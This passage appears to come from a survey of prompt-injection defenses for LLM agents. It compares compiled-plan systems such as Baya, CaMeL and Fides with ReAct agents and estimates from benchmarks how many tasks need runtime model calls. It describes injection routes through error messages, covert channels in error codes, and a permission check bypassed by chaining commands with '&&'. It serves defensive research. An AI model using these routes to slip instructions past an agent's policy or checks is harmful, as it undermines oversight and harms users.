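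This channel is secure only if error messages never include content from the website. Ordinary web software often repeats a rejected value in its error messages. Suppose a customer chose an instruction as their display name, and the refund tool reported "no account found for" followed by the name. The instruction would then reach the planner, which can use every operation available for that site. Chow and colleagues require the site's trusted interface to exclude such text, and treat an interface that doesn't as outside their threat model. They built the interfaces by hand for a few test sites. Someone would have to check the error messages for every new site, and again whenever a site changed.

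Even a clean error can carry a few bits, like the typed error codes discussed earlier, and repeated repairs can carry more. With eight possible errors and three repairs, an attacker who could influence which error occurs would have 8³ = 512 error sequences to choose from, enough to encode nine bits.

Randori tests and repairs each draft program in a simulated world, where every response is trustworthy, and runs it on real data only once it works. Garby and colleagues needed this because in LLMbda an error caused by untrusted data would make the repaired program untrusted too, so it could not make payments.

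Practice in a simulation covers only the rules its designers knew about, while Baya's repairs are most useful for rules that nobody documented, such as a shop's requirement that clothing have a size. But a live failure can leave a job half done. If the refund program fails at message 17, it may already have paid several customers, and a replacement that starts from message 1 has to avoid paying them twice.

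### Mistaken policies and permitted harm

Every guarantee in this section is relative to a policy, and the software that enforces the policy may have bugs. Zhou and colleagues cite a bug in Claude Code from March 2026. Its permission rules checked only the first of several commands joined by `&&`, so a forbidden command could run if it came later. A type checker avoids this mistake because it examines the whole program. Garby and colleagues found a similar bug in CaMeL, whose interpreter treated an untrusted value as trusted once a program had inserted it into text.

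No proof can detect that a policy is wrong. If a developer labels a price list as trusted because it is stored on the company's own server, but forgets that suppliers can edit it, every supplier can influence the agent's purchases even though all the label checks pass. Kravchenko and colleagues likewise assume that each tool behaves as declared.

A policy can also allow actions that are acceptable individually but not in total. If every sub-agent may make one $50 payment, the possible loss depends on the number of sub-agents. Zhou and colleagues mention types that would limit resources or permit an action only once, but leave them for future work. APPA can base its rules on a running total of spending if the developer supplies one.

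Labels also don't capture the purpose of an action. Suppose a sub-agent has read a customer's complaint and is allowed to reply to that customer. It can send an accurate answer or promise a refund that the shop will never pay. Both replies have the same label because they have the same sources and recipient.

A shop owner who approves a policy instead of a plan therefore has to consider every combination of actions the policy permits. She can still do this with the `Shop` library, because the old $2,500 limit holds however many times the sub-agents call themselves. If the developer added a function that could email anyone, she would also have to consider everything the sub-agents could look up and everyone they could send it to.

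## How many tasks need a model call at runtime

Most of the restrictions in the last two sections exist because models read untrusted text while a plan is running, and many plans may not need a model at that stage. Piet and colleagues estimated how many web tasks need one by going through all 860 tasks in WebArena, a benchmark in which agents use simulated websites: an online shop, its administration pages, a forum, a map, Wikipedia and GitLab, where programmers share code. They concluded that 699 tasks (81%) need no model call at runtime and 161 (19%) do. They found no task that needs a new plan partway through.

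### Three kinds of task

The annotators assumed that every site offers a complete and trustworthy set of named operations, such as searching the catalog or adding an item to the cart. For each task, they asked whether a planner could write the program in advance from the user's request and the list of operations alone. They sorted the tasks into three categories:

- *Safe* tasks need only ordinary code. To put the best noise-canceling headphones under $200 in the cart, a program can search, discard anything too expensive, sort by rating and add the top result. Finding the customer with the most canceled orders takes only counting.
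- *Safe-with-influence* tasks need quarantined calls, but the planner can still write every step in advance. One task asks for the cheapest dock with at least 11 slots, which sellers describe in many different ways. Another asks which customers are dissatisfied with a product.
- *Replan-needed* tasks get their steps from text that the program finds while it runs. The example is "read my emails and complete all the action items inside them".

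The refund program would count as "safe with influence". "Safe" here means only safe from prompt injection, so a seller who posts fake ratings could still get the wrong headphones into the cart.

The share of tasks that need a model call ranges from 9% on GitLab to 91% on Wikipedia, where the answers are in ordinary prose. The other four sites fall between 18% and 21%. Wikipedia accounts for only 23 of the 860 tasks.

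Some of the 161 tasks may not need a model call at runtime. Examples among the map tasks include working out that "Liberty Bell city" means Philadelphia and naming the top computer science school in Massachusetts. The planner is itself a language model and receives the request, so it could write "Philadelphia" straight into the program. If that worked for all 27 map tasks in this category, the total would fall to 134, or 16%.

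One of six annotators labeled each site's tasks, and then all six reviewed and discussed the labels until they agreed. This procedure doesn't measure how often two people labeling the same task separately would have disagreed. The paper argues for compiled programs, so labels from people with no stake in that argument would be useful.

Nobody ran an agent on the tasks for this analysis. Real websites also rarely offer complete interfaces. For example, all 129 of the forum's tasks passed the annotation, but the forum software's own interface has 16 operations, which are enough for only 33% of those tasks.

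### Why no WebArena task needs replanning

The 860 WebArena tasks included no replan-needed tasks. In a random sample of what people ask web agents to do, that result would put the true share of such tasks below about 0.35%, with 95% confidence. But researchers wrote the WebArena tasks, so they aren't a random sample. Each task has an automatic check of the agent's answer or the site's final state, and such a check is easiest to write when the request itself determines the result.

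People surely want to delegate open-ended errands, and "deal with my inbox" would be among their first requests to an assistant. Piet and colleagues accept that such tasks exist and would reserve replanning for them. Their result supports only the claim that agents don't need to replan for web tasks in which the user states what should happen.

The boundary also depends on how many cases a planner covers in advance. Suppose the shop owner says "do whatever these messages ask". A planner can't list every possible request, but it could write a program that has branches for refunds, replacements and delivery questions, and passes everything else to the owner. This fixed plan might handle most of the inbox, but it couldn't carry out a request it has no branch for, such as a customer asking the shop to write to his landlord.

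### What Baya's programs did

Chow and colleagues provide a partial check on these estimates, because their web agent Baya writes and runs such programs. They examined 627 programs for four of the six sites. Only 13 (2.1%) contained a model call, and 11 (1.8%) made the call when they ran. In the other two, the call was a fallback that wasn't needed because ordinary code found the answer first.

| Site | Tasks that need a model call, according to the annotators | Baya programs with a model call | Baya programs with fuzzy text matching |
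|---|---|---|---|
| GitLab | 9% | 0% | 17.6% |
| Shop | 20% | 4.7% | 14.6% |
| Shop administration | 18% | 1.3% | 27.9% |
| Forum | 18% | 2.6% | 3.5% |

The choice of sites explains little of the gap. Baya's programs don't cover Wikipedia or the map, but on the other four sites the annotators thought that 113 of 709 tasks (16%) needed a call. At those rates, about 99 of Baya's 627 programs would have contained a call, 86 more than did.

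Text matching explains more, because Baya has a fuzzy matcher that measures how similar two pieces of text are without calling a model. It can match "furnture" to "furniture", for example. The matcher appears in 105 programs, but not always in place of a model. On GitLab, the number of programs that use it is nearly twice the number of tasks that the annotators thought would need a model, so many of those programs were probably for tasks that the annotators had labeled safe. On the forum, at most 6% of programs use either the matcher or a model, so Baya must have handled most of the forum's safe-with-influence tasks in some simpler way, such as an exact keyword search.

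Baya's planner also has instructions to use the site's own filters and deterministic matching whenever possible, and to call a model only for judgments that code can't make reliably, after narrowing down the candidates. The 2% therefore partly measures how well the planner followed these instructions. The wording of the tasks may matter too, because a clearer request can remove the need for a judgment, and Baya's tests used WebArena Verified, a corrected version of the benchmark with revised requests.

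Leaving out a call can also make the answer wrong. Chow and colleagues give the example of finding reviewers who say a product's ear cups are too small. A keyword search for "small" would run without an error but return an incomplete list. Baya failed on about 22% of the scored tasks, enough that all 86 missing calls could have led to wrong answers.

Probably not all of them did, since programs fail for many other reasons. The scores by site are also inconclusive. Averaged over three models, Baya did worst on the shop (69%), where the annotators expected the most model calls, but best on the forum (85%), where they expected nearly as many. The two papers share several authors, who could find out by scoring the safe-with-influence tasks separately. Until then, a reasonable guess is that between 2% and 16% of the tasks on these four sites need a model at runtime.

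### Accuracy, attacks and time

Chow and colleagues compared Baya with two ReAct agents. One could use only a browser, while the other could also use the same interfaces and site-specific guidance as Baya.

| System | Tasks completed | Attacks that influenced the agent | Time per task | Model cost per task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Baya | 77.8% | 0% | 327 seconds | $0.70 |
| ReAct with browser and interfaces | 66.7% | 16.2% | 87 seconds | $0.34 |
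| ReAct with browser only | 55.1% | 25.5% | 60 seconds | $0.16 |

The interfaces alone appear to help about as much as writing the program in advance, since each adds about 11 percentage points in the table. Baya's lead depends heavily on the model. It beat the better ReAct agent by 22.9 points with Claude Sonnet 4.6 but by only 2.4 with GPT-5.6 Luna.

Some of the lead may come from differences in setup. Baya's models worked inside commercial coding tools and could repair failed programs, whereas the ReAct agents called the models directly and had to stop after 30 steps. Because of the repairs, the 77.8% isn't the score of a strictly fixed plan.

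ReAct did better on some shop tasks because the website offers shortcuts. For example, a customer can reorder an item with one click in the order history, while a program using the API has to look up the customer and the old order, create a cart, add the item, fill in the shipping and billing details, and submit the order.

The attack figures count injections that led the agent to take at least one step toward the attacker's goal. Attackers achieved their goal in only one configuration, a ReAct agent running DeepSeek-V4-Flash on the forum, where 5.6% of attempts succeeded. With Claude Sonnet 4.6 and the interfaces, none of the attacks influenced ReAct either.

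Baya's 0% is expected from its design, because the planner never reads the site and 616 of the 627 programs never passed website text to a model while they ran. The test didn't cover the attacks that remain possible, such as false reviews that mislead a classifier. Baya also completed fewer of the users' own tasks in some of these tests. With Claude on the forum, it completed 61.1%, while the two ReAct agents completed 91.7% and 100%.

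Most of Baya's extra time goes into writing and testing a new program for every task. An earlier version that wrote simpler plans in JSON took only 82 seconds, but it completed fewer tasks on every site with every model. Reusing programs for common tasks would reduce the average time.

These figures exclude the work of building the interfaces. The researchers went through each site's software and documentation by hand, corrected the descriptions of its operations (GitLab alone has 1,028), and wrote browser scripts for anything the site's own interface lacked, such as voting on forum posts.

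### Email, banking and workplace chat

Office tasks need model calls far more often. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, a 2025 paper that introduced the Fides system, classifies the 97 user tasks in AgentDojo. Its percentages work out as follows:

- 26 tasks (27%) need no model to process untrusted text.
- 51 tasks (53%) need a quarantined call, but the sequence of tool calls doesn't depend on the answer.
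- 20 tasks (21%) are *data-dependent*, which means that the sequence of tool calls depends on what the agent reads.

The data-dependent share is 5% for email, calendar and file tasks, 10% for travel, 42.9% for Slack and 43.8% for banking. Many of the banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

Data-dependent is a broader category than replan-needed. One of the paper's examples asks the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if any of them requests a meeting. Fides chooses one tool call at a time, so its planner has to see the yes-or-no answer before it can continue. A planner that writes a whole program can put the choice in a branch:

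```
emails = read_emails(3)
if quarantined("Is there a meeting request?", emails) == "yes":
    details = quarantined("Extract the date, time and people.", emails)
    set_event(details)
```

By the WebArena annotators' standard, this task is safe with influence.

*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) uses a stricter test and counts only six of the same 97 tasks as requiring dynamic planning. A task counts only if an agent could not predict all its actions from the request. "Pay the bill" followed by a file name does not count, because the agent can predict that it will read the file and then send money. Much of the difference between 20 and six probably comes from tasks with branches like the one above.

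Even when a task's sequence of actions is predictable, the details of those actions can depend on content written by strangers. *AutoDojo* (2026), another benchmark of defenses against prompt injection, separates requests that specify everything from those that leave details, such as the amount and recipient of a payment, to outside content. A further category leaves even the choice of action to outside content, as in "Please do all the tasks I have on my TODO list". Defenses were less effective on requests that left more open.

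Benchmarks contain few tasks of this last kind. The survey *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) found that the tasks in current benchmarks are mostly static, meaning that later actions depend only on the user's first request. A defense that sticks to its initial plan will therefore do better on these benchmarks than in an office where people often write "see my notes in the attached file".

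### Tasks written to require replanning

Li and colleagues wrote 60 tasks to fill this gap, 20 each for shopping, GitHub and daily life. All require the agent to adapt to what it finds, and each includes at least one helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page that asks the user to log in first. The tasks take 7.1 steps on average, about twice as many as AgentDojo's. CaMeL, which had done well on AgentDojo, completed far fewer of these tasks because it relied on its initial plan.

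The benchmark can't show how common such tasks are, because its tasks were selected for this property. Fixed plans may also be able to handle more of these tasks than the benchmark suggests. A planner could use general knowledge of checkouts to include a branch for logging in, just as the plans in the computer-use study included branches for cookie banners. The main comparison of defenses used GPT-4o, a model from 2024, and newer planners might well include branches for more situations.

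The GitHub tasks involve managing repositories more than writing code. Programming probably needs replanning far more often, because a developer rarely knows what a failing test will reveal. Sumner kept having Claude rewrite the workflow scripts during his port of Bun, which fits this pattern, but one project is little evidence of how often this happens.

### Computer use

Computer-use agents need a model call even to find a button. But Foerster and colleagues conclude that computer tasks depend less on what the agent sees than they appear to, because a planner can predict most situations that arise.

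The test used OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop programs. UI-TARS, a small open model, solved 60 of the 339 automatically scored tasks as a normal agent. When a separate model wrote the plans in advance and UI-TARS only read the screen, the combined system solved 51 tasks on the first attempt and 77 in at least one of three attempts. Both the extra attempts and the separate planner helped, so this isn't a fair comparison of fixed plans and agent loops. But it shows that fixed plans can handle many tasks that researchers had assumed would need constant replanning.

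The number of tasks that a fixed plan can handle also depends on the planner's instructions. On the 60 tasks that UI-TARS had solved alone, plans written from generic instructions solved 11 within three attempts. When the instructions told the planner to observe the screen and check its assumptions before each action, the plans solved 35. In a smaller comparison of nine planning models, the weaker ones often left out branches for unexpected screens.

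### Splitting an open-ended request

Better anticipation doesn't help when the text specifies the actions, as with a to-do list. If a compiled program can't handle something it finds, Chow and colleagues would have Baya stop, explain the problem and let the user make a new request.

The shop owner could handle "do whatever these messages ask" in much the same way. A program would use a quarantined call to list what each customer wants, then stop. She would read the list and tell the assistant which requests to carry out, and the planner would write a second program from her instructions. A hostile message could add an item to the list, but the assistant would not act on it unless she asked. If she pasted the whole list into her new request, however, the planner would be reading text that strangers had influenced.
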